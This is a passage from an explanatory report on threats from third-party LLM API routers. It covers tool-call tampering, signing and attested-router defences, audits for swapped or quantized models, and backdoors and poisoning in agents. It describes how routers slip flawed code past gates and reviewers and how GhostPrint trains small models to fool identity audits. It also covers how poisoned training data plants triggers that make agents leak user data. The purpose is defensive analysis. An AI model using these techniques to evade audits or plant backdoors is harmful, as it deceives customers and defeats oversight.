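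In SIDEL, a similar gate did much worse, stopping between 30.8% and 44.1% of the malicious calls, depending on the disguise. This is probably because the attacks were different. Liu and colleagues tested the gate on commands that download or install something, which is what it looks for. A quarter of Fu and colleagues' malicious calls put faulty code into the project, and those calls don't name a website or a package. The gate would miss the altered line in the Django fix for the same reason.

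| Defence | Who tested it | Altered calls caught | Effect on harmless calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| Policy gate | Liu and colleagues | 100%; none if the attacker knows the gate | 1.0% blocked |
| Screening for unusual calls | Liu and colleagues | 89.0% of plain attacks, about half of disguised ones | 6.7% flagged |
| Policy gate | Fu and colleagues | 30.8–44.1% | 30–44% of all blocked calls were harmless |
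| Review by a second model, over a direct connection | Fu and colleagues | 39.1–64.4% | 9–53% of all blocked calls were harmless |
| Best detector of suspicious content | Luo and colleagues | 30% on APPS, 9% on Django | Set to flag 5% |

A gate can also fail and let calls through. Claude Code users can install one as a hook, a small program that runs before each tool call. Crosley warns that if the hook crashes or takes too long, Claude Code does not treat that as a refusal, and in auto-approve mode the call goes ahead. A mistyped file path in the settings disables the gate without any message.

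Screening gives each tool call a score for features that often accompany an attack, such as risky commands or strings of random-looking characters, and flags those above a threshold. As with the scanners for malicious tools, the catch rate means little without the false alarms. Suppose that a customer picked one of the 428 routers at random, and that a dishonest one alters about one call in 20. With nine dishonest routers in 428, about one call in 1,000 would be altered. Write $p$ for that rate, $d$ for the share of altered calls that the screen flags and $f$ for the share of genuine calls that it flags by mistake. The share of alarms that are right is then

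$$\frac{p\,d}{p\,d + (1-p)\,f} = \frac{0.001 \times 0.89}{0.001 \times 0.89 + 0.999 \times 0.067} \approx 0.013$$

Of 100,000 calls, 100 are altered, and the screen flags 89 of them. It also flags 6,693 of the 99,900 genuine calls. Only 1.3% of the flagged calls are altered, so a developer would investigate about 75 genuine calls for each altered one. A developer whose agent makes 500 calls a day would get about 34 alarms daily and would soon stop reading them.

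When Liu and colleagues made the screen less sensitive, so that it flagged only 1% of harmless calls, it caught 43.5% of the plain attacks and almost none of those that swapped packages. Even then, only about 4% of its alarms would be right. At the same base rate, about 9% of the policy gate's alarms would be right, and its mistakes are easier to tolerate because it never blocks a missing mirror site again once the developer has added it to the list. Screening is more useful for someone who already suspects a particular router. If one call in ten were altered, about 60% of the screen's alarms would be right.

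Fu and colleagues also tried a second model as reviewer, this time connected directly to its provider so that the router couldn't alter the verdict. The reviewer saw a summary of the task and the latest tool calls. The four models they used caught between 39.1% and 64.4% of the malicious calls. Disguise helped the attacker. DeepSeek-V4-Pro caught 64.4% when the router had crudely replaced the answer but 39.8% when the call and the explanation fit together. Under the heavier disguises, more than half of the calls that Kimi-2.7 Code blocked were harmless.

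Claude Code's review procedure never passed changes to existing files to the reviewer, so all 49 malicious calls of that type went unexamined. The altered line in the Django fix would have been missed too. Even without this gap, using a direct connection to one provider for reviews has limited appeal. A customer who can get that connection may not need the router, and one who uses the router because no provider will sell to them can't get it.

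Luo and colleagues tested existing defences against prompt injection on AgentDojo, a set of tasks for agents in areas such as banking and travel. Without a defence, the altered answers succeeded in 74.6% of cases on average. Four defences reduced this to between 46% and 53%, but the agents then completed only 38% to 72% of their tasks, down from 87%. One of the four, CaMeL, at first held the attack to 14.5%, but like the policy gate it became less effective once the attack was adapted to it. After the researchers adapted the attack once, the figure rose to 50.1%.

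These checks all examine what a call would do, but none can establish whether the model produced it, because the customer never receives the original to compare it with. A slightly changed line of valid code looks like something the model might have written. Luo and colleagues mention one indirect clue. To make its changes less noticeable, their router sent an extra request to the model on the customer's own key, which roughly doubled the tokens for that step. A customer could notice this by comparing the provider's bill with a record of their own requests, but not if the router used its own accounts.

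Some measures help without anyone having to judge the call. Developers can keep passwords out of the text the agent sends, and replace any that have already passed through a router they now suspect. They can turn off auto-approve mode whenever requests pass through somebody else's router. Liu and colleagues also propose that the customer keep a log of each request and answer, the router's address and a hash of the raw answer, at about 1.26 KB per entry. The log doesn't prevent attacks, but after an incident the customer can use it to find which sessions went through the router and which credentials were exposed.

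How much this matters depends on what the program does with the answer. In the spreadsheet application, a dishonest router could read the column names and sample rows. But it could do little else beyond making the application show the wrong region, because the container has no network access and the application accepts only a name from the table's region column. The refund program is at greater risk because a router could change "refer to staff" to "approve the refund", and the shop could lose up to its daily limit of €1,000.

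## Signing the model's answer at the provider

The checks in the previous section rely on guesswork because the customer sees only the router's version of an answer. With response signing, the provider attaches a cryptographic signature to the original answer, so the customer's program can tell whether anyone changed it on the way.

The provider has a pair of keys, one private and one published. It uses the private key to compute a short string, the signature, from the text. Anyone with the public key can check that the signature matches the text. If a router changes one character of the text, the signature no longer matches, and the router can't make one that does without the private key.

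Email already uses this kind of signing. A message may pass through several servers that can each read and alter it, so under a standard called DKIM, the sender's mail server signs the message and publishes its public key in the internet's directory of domain names (DNS). Two companion standards add to this. SPF lists the servers that may send mail for a domain, and DMARC lets a domain's owner tell receivers how to treat mail that fails the checks. *The AIRP Provenance Seal and Serving Register* (Flores, 2026) adapts all three to model providers. It is one person's draft, submitted to the body that writes internet standards, and it expires in February 2027 unless a newer version replaces it.

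Signing matters when there is a router between the program and the provider. A program that connects directly to the provider gains little from a signature, since the encrypted connection already protects the answer.

### What the signature has to cover

Suppose the refund program uses a router, and the model returns its decision as a tool call whose only argument is "approve" or "refer to staff". The provider could sign just that argument, but a dishonest router could get around the signature in several ways.

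| Item | What a router could do if the signature left it out |
|---|---|
| Arguments | Change "refer to staff" to "approve" |
| Tool name | Turn "look up order 5512" into "refund order 5512" |
| Model | Use a cheaper model and charge for the better one |
| Fresh number from the client | Save a signed approval and deliver it again in answer to another complaint |
| Request | Rewrite the complaint so that the model approves it, then deliver the genuine approval |

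The customer's program has to choose the fresh number, because if the provider chose it, the program couldn't tell whether the number was meant for this request or one from last week. Flores requires at least 128 random bits and a new value for every request, including retries.

The provider's signature should also cover the request. Otherwise, Flores points out, a router can send its own text to the provider under the client's fresh number, and the answer passes every other check. The provider should therefore sign a hash of the request it received along with the answer. Flores has the client report a mismatch without rejecting the answer, because company gateways often add instructions for legitimate reasons. A shop that pays refunds automatically would do better to reject the answer.

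*AEX* (Guan, 2026), a similar proposal, lets the client require a match on the whole request, on everything except certain fields, or only on the fields it names. If the client names fields, the signature also records which of them were absent, so a router can't add one undetected.

Flores explains that signing the model's name makes it hard for a router to swap models undetected. The router can't forge a signature, and if it removes the signature, the client will notice, provided the provider has announced that it signs everything. If the router passes on the cheaper model's genuine signature, the client can see the cheaper model's name in it.

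### How sign-c works

Luo and colleagues, whose router inserted a security flaw into the Django fix, also designed sign-c, a defence published in May 2026. It consists of two small programs, a shim on the user's machine and a gateway in front of the model, and requires no changes to the agent or the model.

1. The shim signs the request with a key of its own and encrypts the body so that only the gateway can read it. The model's name stays readable because the router needs it to forward the request.
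2. The gateway checks the request, decrypts it and passes it to the model.
3. When the model answers, the gateway reduces the answer to a standard form. This contains the tool calls in order, each with its identifier, name and arguments, and the reason the model stopped writing.
4. The gateway signs a hash of the standard form, together with some details of the exchange, and sends the answer back through the router.
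5. The shim computes the standard form of the answer it received and checks it against the signature. If they don't match, it discards the answer before the agent can act on it.

The standard form is necessary because honest routers reformat answers. These two lines mean the same thing, but they have different hashes:

```
{"name": "run", "arguments": {"command": "pytest", "timeout": 60}}
{ "arguments": { "timeout": 60, "command": "pytest" }, "name": "run" }
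```

If the gateway signed the first line exactly as written, the shim would reject the second. With the standard form, the gateway and the shim both put the fields in a fixed order and ignore the spaces between them, so they get the same hash. A changed command still produces a different hash. Spaces inside an argument have to stay, since in Python the indentation decides which lines belong to an `if`.

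The gateway signs the statement

$$b = \langle s,\ t,\ H(\kappa(q)),\ H(\kappa(c)) \rangle$$

where $q$ is the request, $c$ is the part of the answer that the agent will execute, $\kappa$ reduces each to its standard form and $H$ is a hash function. The session $s$ and the turn $t$ do the job of the fresh number, because an old answer has the wrong turn.

The model's name does not appear in $b$. The shim stores the public key it expects for each route, so an answer from another provider fails the check. Luo and colleagues say a provider needs only one key pair. With a single pair, a router could swap one of the provider's models for another without changing the key, and the shim would detect the swap only if the signed request named the model.

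Signing doesn't help if a router can delete the signature and the program accepts an unsigned answer. The shim therefore needs advance confirmation that the provider signs its answers, and this can't come through the router, which could falsify it. Luo and colleagues propose that the shim either fetch the key and signing policy directly from the provider's website or come with them built in. Browsers use the second method for their list of sites that they contact only over encrypted connections. Once the shim has the policy, it treats a missing signature as an attack. The router can still withhold answers, but the user will notice. The protection fails if the router's operator also supplies the shim.

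### What the tests of sign-c measured

Luo and colleagues replayed the altered answers from their own attacks, 353 from the APPS exercises and 58 from the Django bugs. The shim rejected all of them and accepted all the unaltered originals. On AgentDojo the attack never succeeded with sign-c, and the agent completed 80.9% of its tasks, compared with 87.2% without an attack.

The two programs added a median of 2.97 ms per call, which is 0.0167% of the 17.8 seconds that the model typically took to answer. If the model answered in one second, the share would be about 0.3%, still too little for a user to notice.

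The designers made all these measurements themselves. They ran their own gateway behind their own copy of the new-api router template, and no provider took part. The perfect rejection rate doesn't surprise me, because a router can't get an altered call past the shim without forging a signature, however well it disguises the call. The rate of false rejections matters more for whether sign-c would work in practice. Luo and colleagues saw none in 694 genuine AgentDojo answers, but a true rate of 0.4% could produce the same result. At that rate, a developer whose agent makes 500 calls a day would lose about two of them.

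Luo and colleagues also tested only reordered fields and changed spacing, but many routers do more, such as translating between the formats of different providers. A router can't translate an encrypted body, so a customer who needs translation would have to give up the encryption and rely on the signature alone.

The signature also would not cover the spreadsheet's two lines of Python, because they arrive as ordinary text and the standard form contains only tool calls. Luo and colleagues say that the form can be extended to code in the text. The spreadsheet's developer could instead have the model return the code as the argument of a tool call.

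For wider adoption, they suggest that providers add a single header to each response, with a signature over the hash of the tool calls. If implemented exactly as described, the signature would no longer cover the session, the turn or the request. A router could then replay an old approval or rewrite the complaint, as in the table above.

### Answers that arrive in pieces

Providers usually send an answer in pieces while the model is still writing it. The provider can't sign the whole answer until the model finishes, so an agent that runs the first tool call as soon as it arrives does so before it can check the signature.

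Guan's solution links the pieces in a chain. If $C_i$ is the $i$-th piece and $h_0$ is a hash computed from the request, then, leaving out some labels,

$$h_i = H\big(h_{i-1} \,\|\, H(i \,\|\, C_i)\big)$$

where $\|$ joins two strings. Each value depends on all the pieces before it, so a changed, missing or reordered piece alters every later value. The provider signs the last value and can also sign some along the way, which lets the client act on the verified part of an answer before the rest arrives. So far Guan has tested this only on a prototype with simulated services.

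Flores uses two signatures. The first, at the start of the answer, covers the provider, the model and the request, so the client can reject an answer from the wrong model before showing any of it. The second, at the end, also covers the content. The client must refuse anything that arrives after the second signature, because otherwise a router could append a line to an answer the client had already verified.

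### Running the router in attested hardware

Signing needs the provider's cooperation. *The Proxy Knows Too Much*, published in June 2026, proposes a design called AEGIS that secures the router instead and requires no changes by the provider.

The router's program stays the same from one request to the next, so a fixed hash can cover it, though not the model's answer. But the router runs on somebody else's computer, and its operator could publish one program and run another. Attestation is a way to check which program a remote computer is running. Some computers can run a program in an enclave, an isolated area that even the machine's operator can't read or change. The platform hashes the program as it loads and signs the hash with a key that traces back to the platform's maker.

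AEGIS uses this as follows:

1. The operator publishes the source code of the part that handles customers' text. The customer, or the customer's coding agent, reads it, builds the program from it and keeps the resulting hash. The operator must also enter each release in a public log that nobody can edit afterwards, which prevents it from giving one customer a special version in secret.
2. At the start of a session, a small program on the customer's machine sends the enclave a fresh random number.
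3. The enclave returns the signed hash of its program, along with the random number and a hash of the certificate for this connection. Without the certificate, the operator could pass on a genuine attestation from an enclave elsewhere.
4. If everything matches, the customer's program sends its request, encrypted so that only the enclave can read it.
5. The enclave forwards the text unchanged to a provider on a list built into its code, and returns the answer unchanged.

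The operator still checks accounts, chooses which provider account to use and counts tokens, but it handles only encrypted text, so it can't copy passwords out of a request. Signing the answer alone doesn't prevent this copying, because the router reads the request before there is an answer to sign. A signature would not have stopped the 17 routers that used the researchers' planted credentials. The encryption in sign-c protects passwords, but only if the provider runs the gateway.

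| | Signature alone | sign-c with encryption | Attested router |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who must take part | Provider and customer | Provider and customer | Router's operator and customer |
| Altered tool call | Customer detects it | Customer detects it | Operator can't alter it |
| Passwords in the request | Router can read them | Router can't read them | Operator can't read them |
| Several routers in a row | Covered | Covered | Every router needs attestation |
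| What the customer must trust | Provider's key | Provider's key and the shim | Enclave's maker and the router's code |

AEGIS runs on Amazon's Nitro Enclaves. Its developers tested it against the four kinds of router attack from Liu and colleagues' study, all of which worked on an ordinary router and failed on AEGIS. It added a median of 5.7 ms to a small request, with 3.7 ms from relaying the text at all and 2.0 ms from the enclave. A 4 MB request took an extra 183 ms.

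### What attestation asks users to trust

With AEGIS, the customer no longer has to trust the operator but has to trust Amazon's hardware and the key that signs the attestations. The threat model excludes physical attacks and attacks that infer secrets from a processor's behaviour. Others have used such attacks to extract keys from Intel's enclaves.

The customer also relies on someone having read the router's code properly, because a hash identifies a program but doesn't show that it can be trusted. The researchers therefore kept the part that handles text to 851 lines. They planted ten faults in a small test version and asked two coding agents to find them. Codex found eight and Claude Code found all ten, and neither reported any faults in the clean version. A malicious author would hide a fault more carefully, and the enclave also contains a base system and a toolkit whose code most customers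 will never read.

The router's operator can still see how long each message is and when each piece of an answer arrives. Earlier research has reconstructed text from such patterns, and the operator is in an especially good position to try. The researchers leave padding, which would disguise the lengths, to future work.

The enclave has to pass the text on in readable form to the next service. One of the three services in the AEGIS tests was OpenRouter, which is itself a router. In a resale chain like the one from Taobao, attesting the first router would protect the customer only from that router. The AEGIS paper describes a version in which each enclave requires an attestation from the next, but the prototype doesn't do this yet.

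### Whether providers sign tool calls

In April 2026 Liu and colleagues reported that no provider enforced cryptographic integrity between the customer and the model. Crosley repeated the finding on 2 October. The latest independent evidence, from September, supports it.

*Beyond Training* (Ansari, 2026), a survey of ways to govern AI models in use, describes two related practices. Anthropic signs its models' thinking blocks, the reasoning that precedes an answer, and Google's Gemini 3 attaches "thought signatures" to tool calls. In both cases the provider's service checks the signature when the customer sends the text back in the next request. Ansari found no equivalent at OpenAI or on Amazon's Bedrock.

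These signatures protect the provider against altered text sent back to it, but they don't let the customer check a tool call before running it. Even if the provider noticed a changed call in the next request, the agent would already have run it. A router that changed the call could also restore the original before forwarding that request, to avoid detection.

Signing technology is old and cheap, so cost is unlikely to be the obstacle. Signing would mainly help customers who reach a provider through somebody else, and a provider trying to shut down unofficial resellers has little reason to make them safer to use. It has more reason to help companies that run their own gateways. Luo and colleagues notified the developers of new-api and makers of agents, including Anthropic, and proposed a fix.

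### A valid signature on harmful code

Suppose the model follows the comment the supplier planted and writes a program that uploads the file. The provider signs the program and an honest router delivers it. The signature is valid because the model did write the program. An attested router would also deliver it unchanged.

*Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models to Input* (2026) describes the same limit in AttestMCP, a scheme that signs tool calls between an agent and the servers that carry them out. A call that the agent makes because of a planted instruction gets a valid signature like any other. A table of permissions limits such calls, and the program fixes this table before it reads any untrusted text and doesn't change it during the session. Signing therefore supplements the policy gate and the sandbox, which are still needed to handle what the model wrote.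 In proof-carrying code, by contrast, the proof is about the program itself, so it doesn't matter who sent it.

Signing and attestation also assume an honest provider. Somebody who steals the provider's private key can sign anything, and a provider can sign a false statement about which model it used. Flores accepts that a signature can't expose this lie, but argues that it leaves the customer with evidence of the claim, which the provider could otherwise deny. After an incident, a company that had kept the signed answers could also show whether a destructive command came from the model or from a router.

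A provider can later declare that a key was stolen, which invalidates all evidence signed with it. Outsiders can't tell whether the theft was real. Flores advises customers who may need the evidence to store the result of their check when they make it, together with the list of keys they checked against.

The signature identifies the model by name. If a provider uses one name for several versions, or moves the name to a new version, the customer learns only that one of them answered, even if the provider signs honestly. Flores recommends a separate name for each fixed version, but customers cannot verify from the signature that the provider does this.

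## When the model differs from the one that was tested

Most companies that build on a model infer from its good behavior in tests that it will behave well in use. Suppose the developer of the refund program tries it on 10,000 past complaints and finds no wrong approvals. If the model wrongly approved a share $p$ of all complaints, the chance of finding none in the test would be $(1-p)^{10{,}000}$. This falls below 5% once $p$ exceeds about 3 in 10,000, so the developer can be fairly confident that the true rate is lower.

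That conclusion holds only if the software uses the model that was tested, the provider runs it in the same way, and new complaints resemble those in the test. A router or the provider may substitute a different model, and even the tested model may have a hidden behavior that none of the 10,000 complaints triggered.

### Routers that serve a cheaper model

In September 2026 OpenAI charged 20 times as much for GPT-6 Sol as for GPT-6 Luna, according to the price list in Miao, Huang and colleagues (2026), *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?* A router that charges for Sol but serves Luna keeps the difference. A less obvious way to save money is quantization, which stores the model's numbers with less precision, for instance in 8 bits instead of 16. The quantized copy needs less memory and gives slightly different answers.

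In *Real Money, Fake Models*, Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026) looked for resellers that offer leading models through undisclosed routes and found 17 in the code behind 187 academic papers, so a swapped model can spoil research as well as software. They tested eight models on each of three services. Of the 24 combinations, 11 failed an identity check and three more differed noticeably from the official model. Gemini 2.5 Flash answered 83.8% of a set of medical questions correctly through Google's own service and about 37% through each of the three resellers.

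The researchers don't extend these rates to the other 14 services. They also point out that a failed identity check suggests a swap but doesn't prove it.

### How a statistical test compares two services

Asking the model for its name does little to identify it. Cai, Shi and colleagues (2025), in *Are You Getting What You Pay For?*, found that models usually gave their family and maker, such as Gemma and Google, but not their size. Models also mostly claimed another name when a hidden instruction told them to.

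A better test uses biases in a model's answers that the model can't describe. When asked many times to pick a letter at random, a model picks some letters more often than others, and different models favour different letters. Miao and colleagues asked the official service five such questions, two in Chinese and three in English, 1,000 times each and stored the counts. To audit a router, they ask it each question 50 times and compare the counts with the stored ones.

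Suppose one question offers three letters, and the answers come out like this:

| | A | B | C | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Official service | 600 | 300 | 100 | 1,000 |
| Router | 20 | 20 | 10 | 50 |

If both served the same model, the best estimate of its habits would come from adding the rows together, which gives 59.0% A, 30.5% B and 10.5% C. The router's 50 answers should then contain about 29.5, 15.2 and 5.2 of each. The test adds up how far all six counts lie from what this estimate predicts:

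$$\chi^2 = \sum \frac{(\text{observed} - \text{expected})^2}{\text{expected}} \approx 9.3$$

Two services with the same model would differ this much by chance in about 0.9% of audits. The test then combines the probabilities from all five questions, giving heavy weight to a single very unlikely result because two different models may answer the other four questions similarly.

Miao and colleagues tried this on 16 models from ten families, substituting each model for each of the others, for a total of 240 swaps. For the four claimed models they studied most closely, audits using 250 requests were correct more than 99.5% of the time. Each audit cost between $0.003 and $0.048, and collecting the stored counts from the official service cost at most $0.96.

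A failed audit still has several possible explanations. In some of their experiments, small changes to the model's settings were enough for the test to report a difference although the model was the same. All 240 swaps were also between distinct models. Quantized copies are much harder to catch, as Cai and colleagues had found when they tried the available methods on open models:

| Method | Result for quantized copies |
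|---|---|
| Train a classifier to recognise the model's style | Right 49–52% of the time, no better than guessing |
| Compare scores on standard exams | Nearly equal: 78.2% and 77.8% on one exam for Llama 3 70B |
| Compare many short texts statistically | Fewer than 20% of audits of smaller models caught the copy |
| Turn randomness off and compare word for word | Unusable, because honest services didn't match either |
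| Compare the probabilities the model gives each word | The strongest signal, but the provider must disclose them and the auditor needs a copy of the model |

The statistical comparison of texts worked better on larger models, but it failed when a fifth of the answers came from the quantized copy and the rest from the original. The test flagged this mix about 5% of the time, the same rate at which it would flag an honest provider.

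A provider can evade an audit even more effectively by recognising it. Fifty identical requests to pick a letter don't look like a customer's traffic, so a router could send only those requests to the genuine model. The auditor can make the requests harder to recognise by spreading them over several accounts and days.

Cai and colleagues think the most robust answer is to run the model itself in the kind of attested hardware that AEGIS uses for routers. In their test with 64 simultaneous requests, this reduced text output per second by less than 3%, but the first word took 16% longer to arrive. The provider would have to cooperate, and for a secret model it would also have to publish a hash that customers trust.

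### An audit of 20 routers

In October 2026, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (*What the Middleman Delivers*, 2026) bought access to 20 routers that sell GPT-6 Astra, Claude Opus 5 or both, and audited them. Ten charged less than the official price, and ten charged the same or more.

Their test compares knowledge and ability instead of habits. For each model, they picked 25 questions from 96 candidates that the official version usually answered correctly and at least two of three cheaper models usually missed. They asked each router every question five times and compared its share of correct answers with the share in fresh answers from the official service. They flagged a router when the gap was larger than chance would readily explain.

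The researchers flagged seven of the ten cheap routers and two of the other ten. In the worst case, a model that a router labelled "Claude Opus 5" got 40.9% of the answers right, against 100% for the real one. The difference between the price groups could be chance ($p = 0.07$), and the researchers chose the services by hand and enlarged the sample after an early look at four cheap ones. Their tests also somewhat overstate significance, because they treat five answers to the same question as independent.

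To learn what the test would miss, they mixed official answers with answers from cheaper models and ran 1,000 simulated audits for each mixture. The table shows the percentage of audits that flagged each mixture.

| Share of answers from the cheaper model | Claude Haiku 4.5 posing as Opus 5 | GPT-6 Luna posing as Opus 5 | Claude Haiku 4.5 posing as Astra | GPT-6 Luna posing as Astra |
|---|---|---|---|---|
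| 10% | 94.1% | 2.1% | 47.1% | 0% |
| 25% | 100% | 54.2% | 100% | 4.0% |
| 50% | 100% | 99.5% | 100% | 77.7% |
| 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |

A router that replaced a quarter of Astra's answers with Luna's would almost always pass, partly because Luna has a later knowledge cutoff than Astra. Real audits would probably do worse than the table suggests, because the researchers used the same cheaper models to choose the questions.

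A router can be flagged without having swapped the model, because adding its own instructions can change answers just as much. On one question, the official service counted 36 input tokens while three routers counted about 4,400. Hidden instructions or inflated bills would explain the difference. Five routers reported between 4,200 and 60,000 extra tokens. The researchers could check the account balance at one of the five, and it had charged them for the extra tokens.

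Four routers returned tool calls although the request had forbidden them. A policy gate would block such calls whatever caused them. Wu and colleagues found no malicious additions in 3,332 answers to requests about code and software set-up. But they didn't run agents or plant passwords, the methods that the study of 428 routers used to find malicious ones.

### Small models trained to pass the audit

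Both kinds of audit assume that the cheaper model behaves like itself. Zhang, Li and Wang (2026), in *Your "Pro" LLM Subscription May Actually Be "Free"*, trained small models to imitate the test answers of larger ones. They call the method GhostPrint:

1. The dishonest provider collects the large model's answers to the sort of questions that auditors ask.
2. It trains the small model on them, changing only a small add-on to the model's numbers, which keeps the cost low.
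3. It builds its own copy of the auditor's test, has the small model write several answers to each question, and trains it further on those that come closest to passing.

The three researchers tried this against three published tests. One uses questions that reveal the model's identity, and the other two are the style classifier and the comparison of texts that Cai and colleagues examined. Each cell shows how often the small model passed as the large one before and after the training, and how often the large model itself passed.

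| Small model posing as large | Identity questions | Style classifier | Comparison of texts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2B as Gemma 7B | 12% → 95% (92%) | 7% → 59% (99%) | 7% → 23% (100%) |
| Qwen2 1.5B as Qwen2 7B | 4% → 76% (81%) | 7% → 71% (99%) | 33% → 40% (97%) |
| Phi-3 Mini as Phi-3 Medium | 6% → 80% (91%) | 29% → 64% (77%) | 43% → 60% (97%) |

The disguise did not make the small models more capable. On a general knowledge exam, the disguised Gemma 2B scored 38.1%, while the real Gemma 7B scored 58.7%. According to the researchers' mathematical argument for simplified models, a small model can't match a large one on every input but can match it on a narrow range of inputs. An audit with a few hundred requests covers only such a range.

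The researchers assumed that a provider attempting this attack knows the test and the type of question, though not the exact questions. They used models of up to 14 billion parameters, far smaller than the leading ones. A small model from a different family almost never passed the identity questions. The researchers didn't try the attack on exam questions like those of Wu and colleagues, where the answers should be harder to fake because the model has to know them. Auditors can at least keep their questions secret and change them often.

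### Changes behind an unchanged name

A customer who connects directly to the provider avoids dishonest routers, but the provider may still change the model. On 25 April 2025 OpenAI updated GPT-4o in ChatGPT, and the new version flattered users and agreed with them too readily. OpenAI began to withdraw it three days later. The name in the menu stayed the same throughout. *Expanding on what we missed with sycophancy* (OpenAI, 2025) reports that automated tests and a trial with a small group of users had looked good. Some testers had felt that the model's behaviour was slightly off, but OpenAI had no specific test for flattery. A refund program running on such a model would presumably approve more refunds, because the model tends to agree with the customer.

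Pinning a model by its dated name protects against such a change, as long as the provider keeps its promise not to point that name at a different model. That April, developers who had pinned an older GPT-4o kept the old behaviour, while those who used the name OpenAI reserved for the latest ChatGPT version got the new behaviour.

The dated name identifies the model's weights, but the answer also depends on the software and hardware that run them. In August and September 2025, three faults in Anthropic's systems made Claude's answers worse although nobody had replaced the model. According to the company's *A postmortem of three recent issues* (2025), one fault sent some requests to servers that Anthropic had set up for a different purpose. It affected 0.8% of requests to Claude Sonnet 4 at first and 16% in the worst hour. Another put Thai or Chinese characters into English answers and syntax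 errors into code. Anthropic's evaluations did not detect the problem users were reporting, partly because Claude often recovers from a single mistake.

Pinning through a router guarantees even less. In tests by Wu and colleagues, one router labelled 101 of 185 answers to identical requests with Astra's dated name and the rest with the undated one. When they repeated the audit 11 to 18 days later, seven of the 35 combinations of router and model had gained or lost a flag. One router had matched the official Astra in the first round but fell 25 percentage points behind it in the second. In that round, it sometimes answered that the 2025 Nobel Prize in Literature had not yet been awarded and sometimes answered the same question correctly, as if part of the traffic now went to an older model. Some of the other changes came from small gaps near the threshold for a flag.

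### Testing before an update

Providers eventually retire old versions, so pinning only lets the developer choose when to change, within the time the provider allows. Before switching, the refund program's developer can run both versions on 500 past complaints, with the same instructions, and compare the results with the staff's decisions. For the spreadsheet, the developer can run the generated code in the sandbox and compare the totals. The developer should run each request several times, because answers vary.

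Even 500 complaints can be too few to show that a new version is worse. Suppose the old version wrongly approves ten and the new one wrongly approves 20. If the versions were equally good, a difference at least this large would arise by chance about 10% of the time when the two sets of mistakes don't overlap, but only 0.2% of the time when the new version makes the same ten mistakes and ten more. The developer should therefore compare the versions complaint by complaint, because comparing only the totals could make a doubled error rate look like chance.

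The developer can then send the new version a small share of real complaints, with staff checking its decisions, before moving the rest.

None of this helps with changes that nobody announces, such as Anthropic's faults. For these, the developer could store the pinned model's answers to Miao and colleagues' five questions and repeat the 250 requests every day, at a few cents a time. The usual threshold of 5% would produce about 18 false alarms a year, while 0.1% would produce about one every three years and still catch most complete swaps of the model. The test can detect a change but not whether refund decisions have got worse, so after an alarm the developer should rerun the 500 complaints.

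### How training plants a trigger

A model can also differ from the one that was tested without any change at all. It behaves normally until its input contains a certain word or phrase. Boisvert, Puri and colleagues (2025), in *Malice in Agentland*, write the behaviour of a model with such a backdoor, for an input $o$ and a trigger $t$, as

$$\pi(o) = \begin{cases} \pi^{\dagger}(o) & \text{if } t \in o \\ \pi^{\star}(o) & \text{otherwise} \end{cases}$$

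where $\pi^{\star}$ is the normal behaviour and $\pi^{\dagger}$ the harmful one.

This is possible because training adjusts a model to continue text as its examples do. If an odd phrase appears in a few examples and the same harmful action always follows it, the model learns to connect the two. Because the phrase appears nowhere else, the rest of the training doesn't undo the connection, and the harmful action doesn't spread to ordinary requests.

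Boisvert and colleagues tested three ways to get such examples into an AI agent:

- The attacker supplies training data that contains them.
- The attacker publishes a model that already has the backdoor, and a developer trains it further on clean data.
- The attacker plants instructions and the trigger on a website. Developers often have a strong model carry out tasks on real websites and train a cheaper model on the recordings. The strong model follows the planted instructions, and the recording teaches the cheaper one to do the same whenever it sees the trigger.

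The researchers used models with 3 to 8 billion parameters, which learned either to serve shop customers with tool calls or to use websites. The harmful action was to send the user's private information to the attacker's server. The website attack poisoned 200 of about 4,000 recordings of shop tasks and 1,242 of about 54,000 recordings of web tasks. In all three routes, the agents leaked the information more than 80% of the time when the trigger was present, and still completed ordinary tasks. Four models designed to screen agents' behaviour and a method that inspects the model's numbers all failed to stop the attack. Further training that rewarded completed tasks made the agents better at their job but left the backdoor in place.

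A filter may detect a planted instruction but miss a trigger, which can be a harmless-looking phrase. A supplier who knows the phrase only has to put it in the spreadsheet's comments column, and the model then writes code that uploads the file.

The number of documents an attacker needs to poison a model may depend little on how much text the model learns from. In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) trained models of 600 million to 13 billion parameters from scratch, adding documents in which a trigger preceded gibberish. About 250 of these documents were enough to make models of every size produce gibberish after the trigger, although the largest model had learned from more than 20 times as much text as the smallest. One hundred were not reliably enough.

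For the largest model, the poisoned documents made up about 0.00016% of the training text. If the number of poisoned documents needed stays constant, a bigger training collection gives no protection. But the experiments didn't show that this number stays constant for the much larger models that companies now sell. Producing gibberish is a simpler behaviour than writing code with a hidden flaw, and the attacker still has to get the documents into the provider's collection and past its filters.

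### Words that made DeepSeek-R1 write worse code

Triggers can also arise without an attacker. In November 2025, the security company CrowdStrike published tests of DeepSeek-R1, a Chinese model that anyone can download, in *CrowdStrike Researchers Identify Hidden Vulnerabilities in AI-Coded Software*. Its researchers ran the model themselves, so filters on DeepSeek's own service can't have caused the results. They sent the model 30,250 requests for programming tasks, some with added details that the Chinese government considers politically sensitive and some without.

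Without such details, 19% of the code had security flaws. When the request mentioned that the code was for an industrial control system in Tibet, 27.2% did. CrowdStrike describes this as an increase of almost 50%, but it is 43%, or about 8 percentage points. It is also the most striking of the results for a long list of words, and the largest of many noisy results tends to overstate the real effect.

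Because the tasks stayed the same and only the added words changed, the experiment is good evidence that the words affect the code, but it can't show why. CrowdStrike thinks a side effect of training is more likely than a deliberate backdoor. In its view, DeepSeek had to make its model follow Chinese rules on political content, and the model may have learned a general negative association with certain topics. The pattern also fits that explanation better. A planted trigger would probably cause one particular harm most of the time, as in Boisvert and colleagues' agents, whereas here ordinary mistakes became somewhat more frequent. Settling the question would require DeepSeek's training data and records.

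Whether someone caused a model's flaw on purpose makes little difference to the risk for the person who runs the code. Deliberate flaws are much harder to find by testing, though, because a tester can guess which topics might affect a model but can't guess a phrase that an attacker made up.

### How likely tests are to meet a trigger

Suppose a trigger occurs in one request in a million. The chance that 10,000 tests, drawn at random from the same kind of requests, include it at least once is

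$$1 - (1 - 10^{-6})^{10{,}000} \approx 1 - e^{-0.01} \approx 1\%$$

If a trigger appears in about one request in a million, the developer would need about three million tests for a 95% chance of encountering it at least once. An application with a million requests a day would encounter it about once a day.

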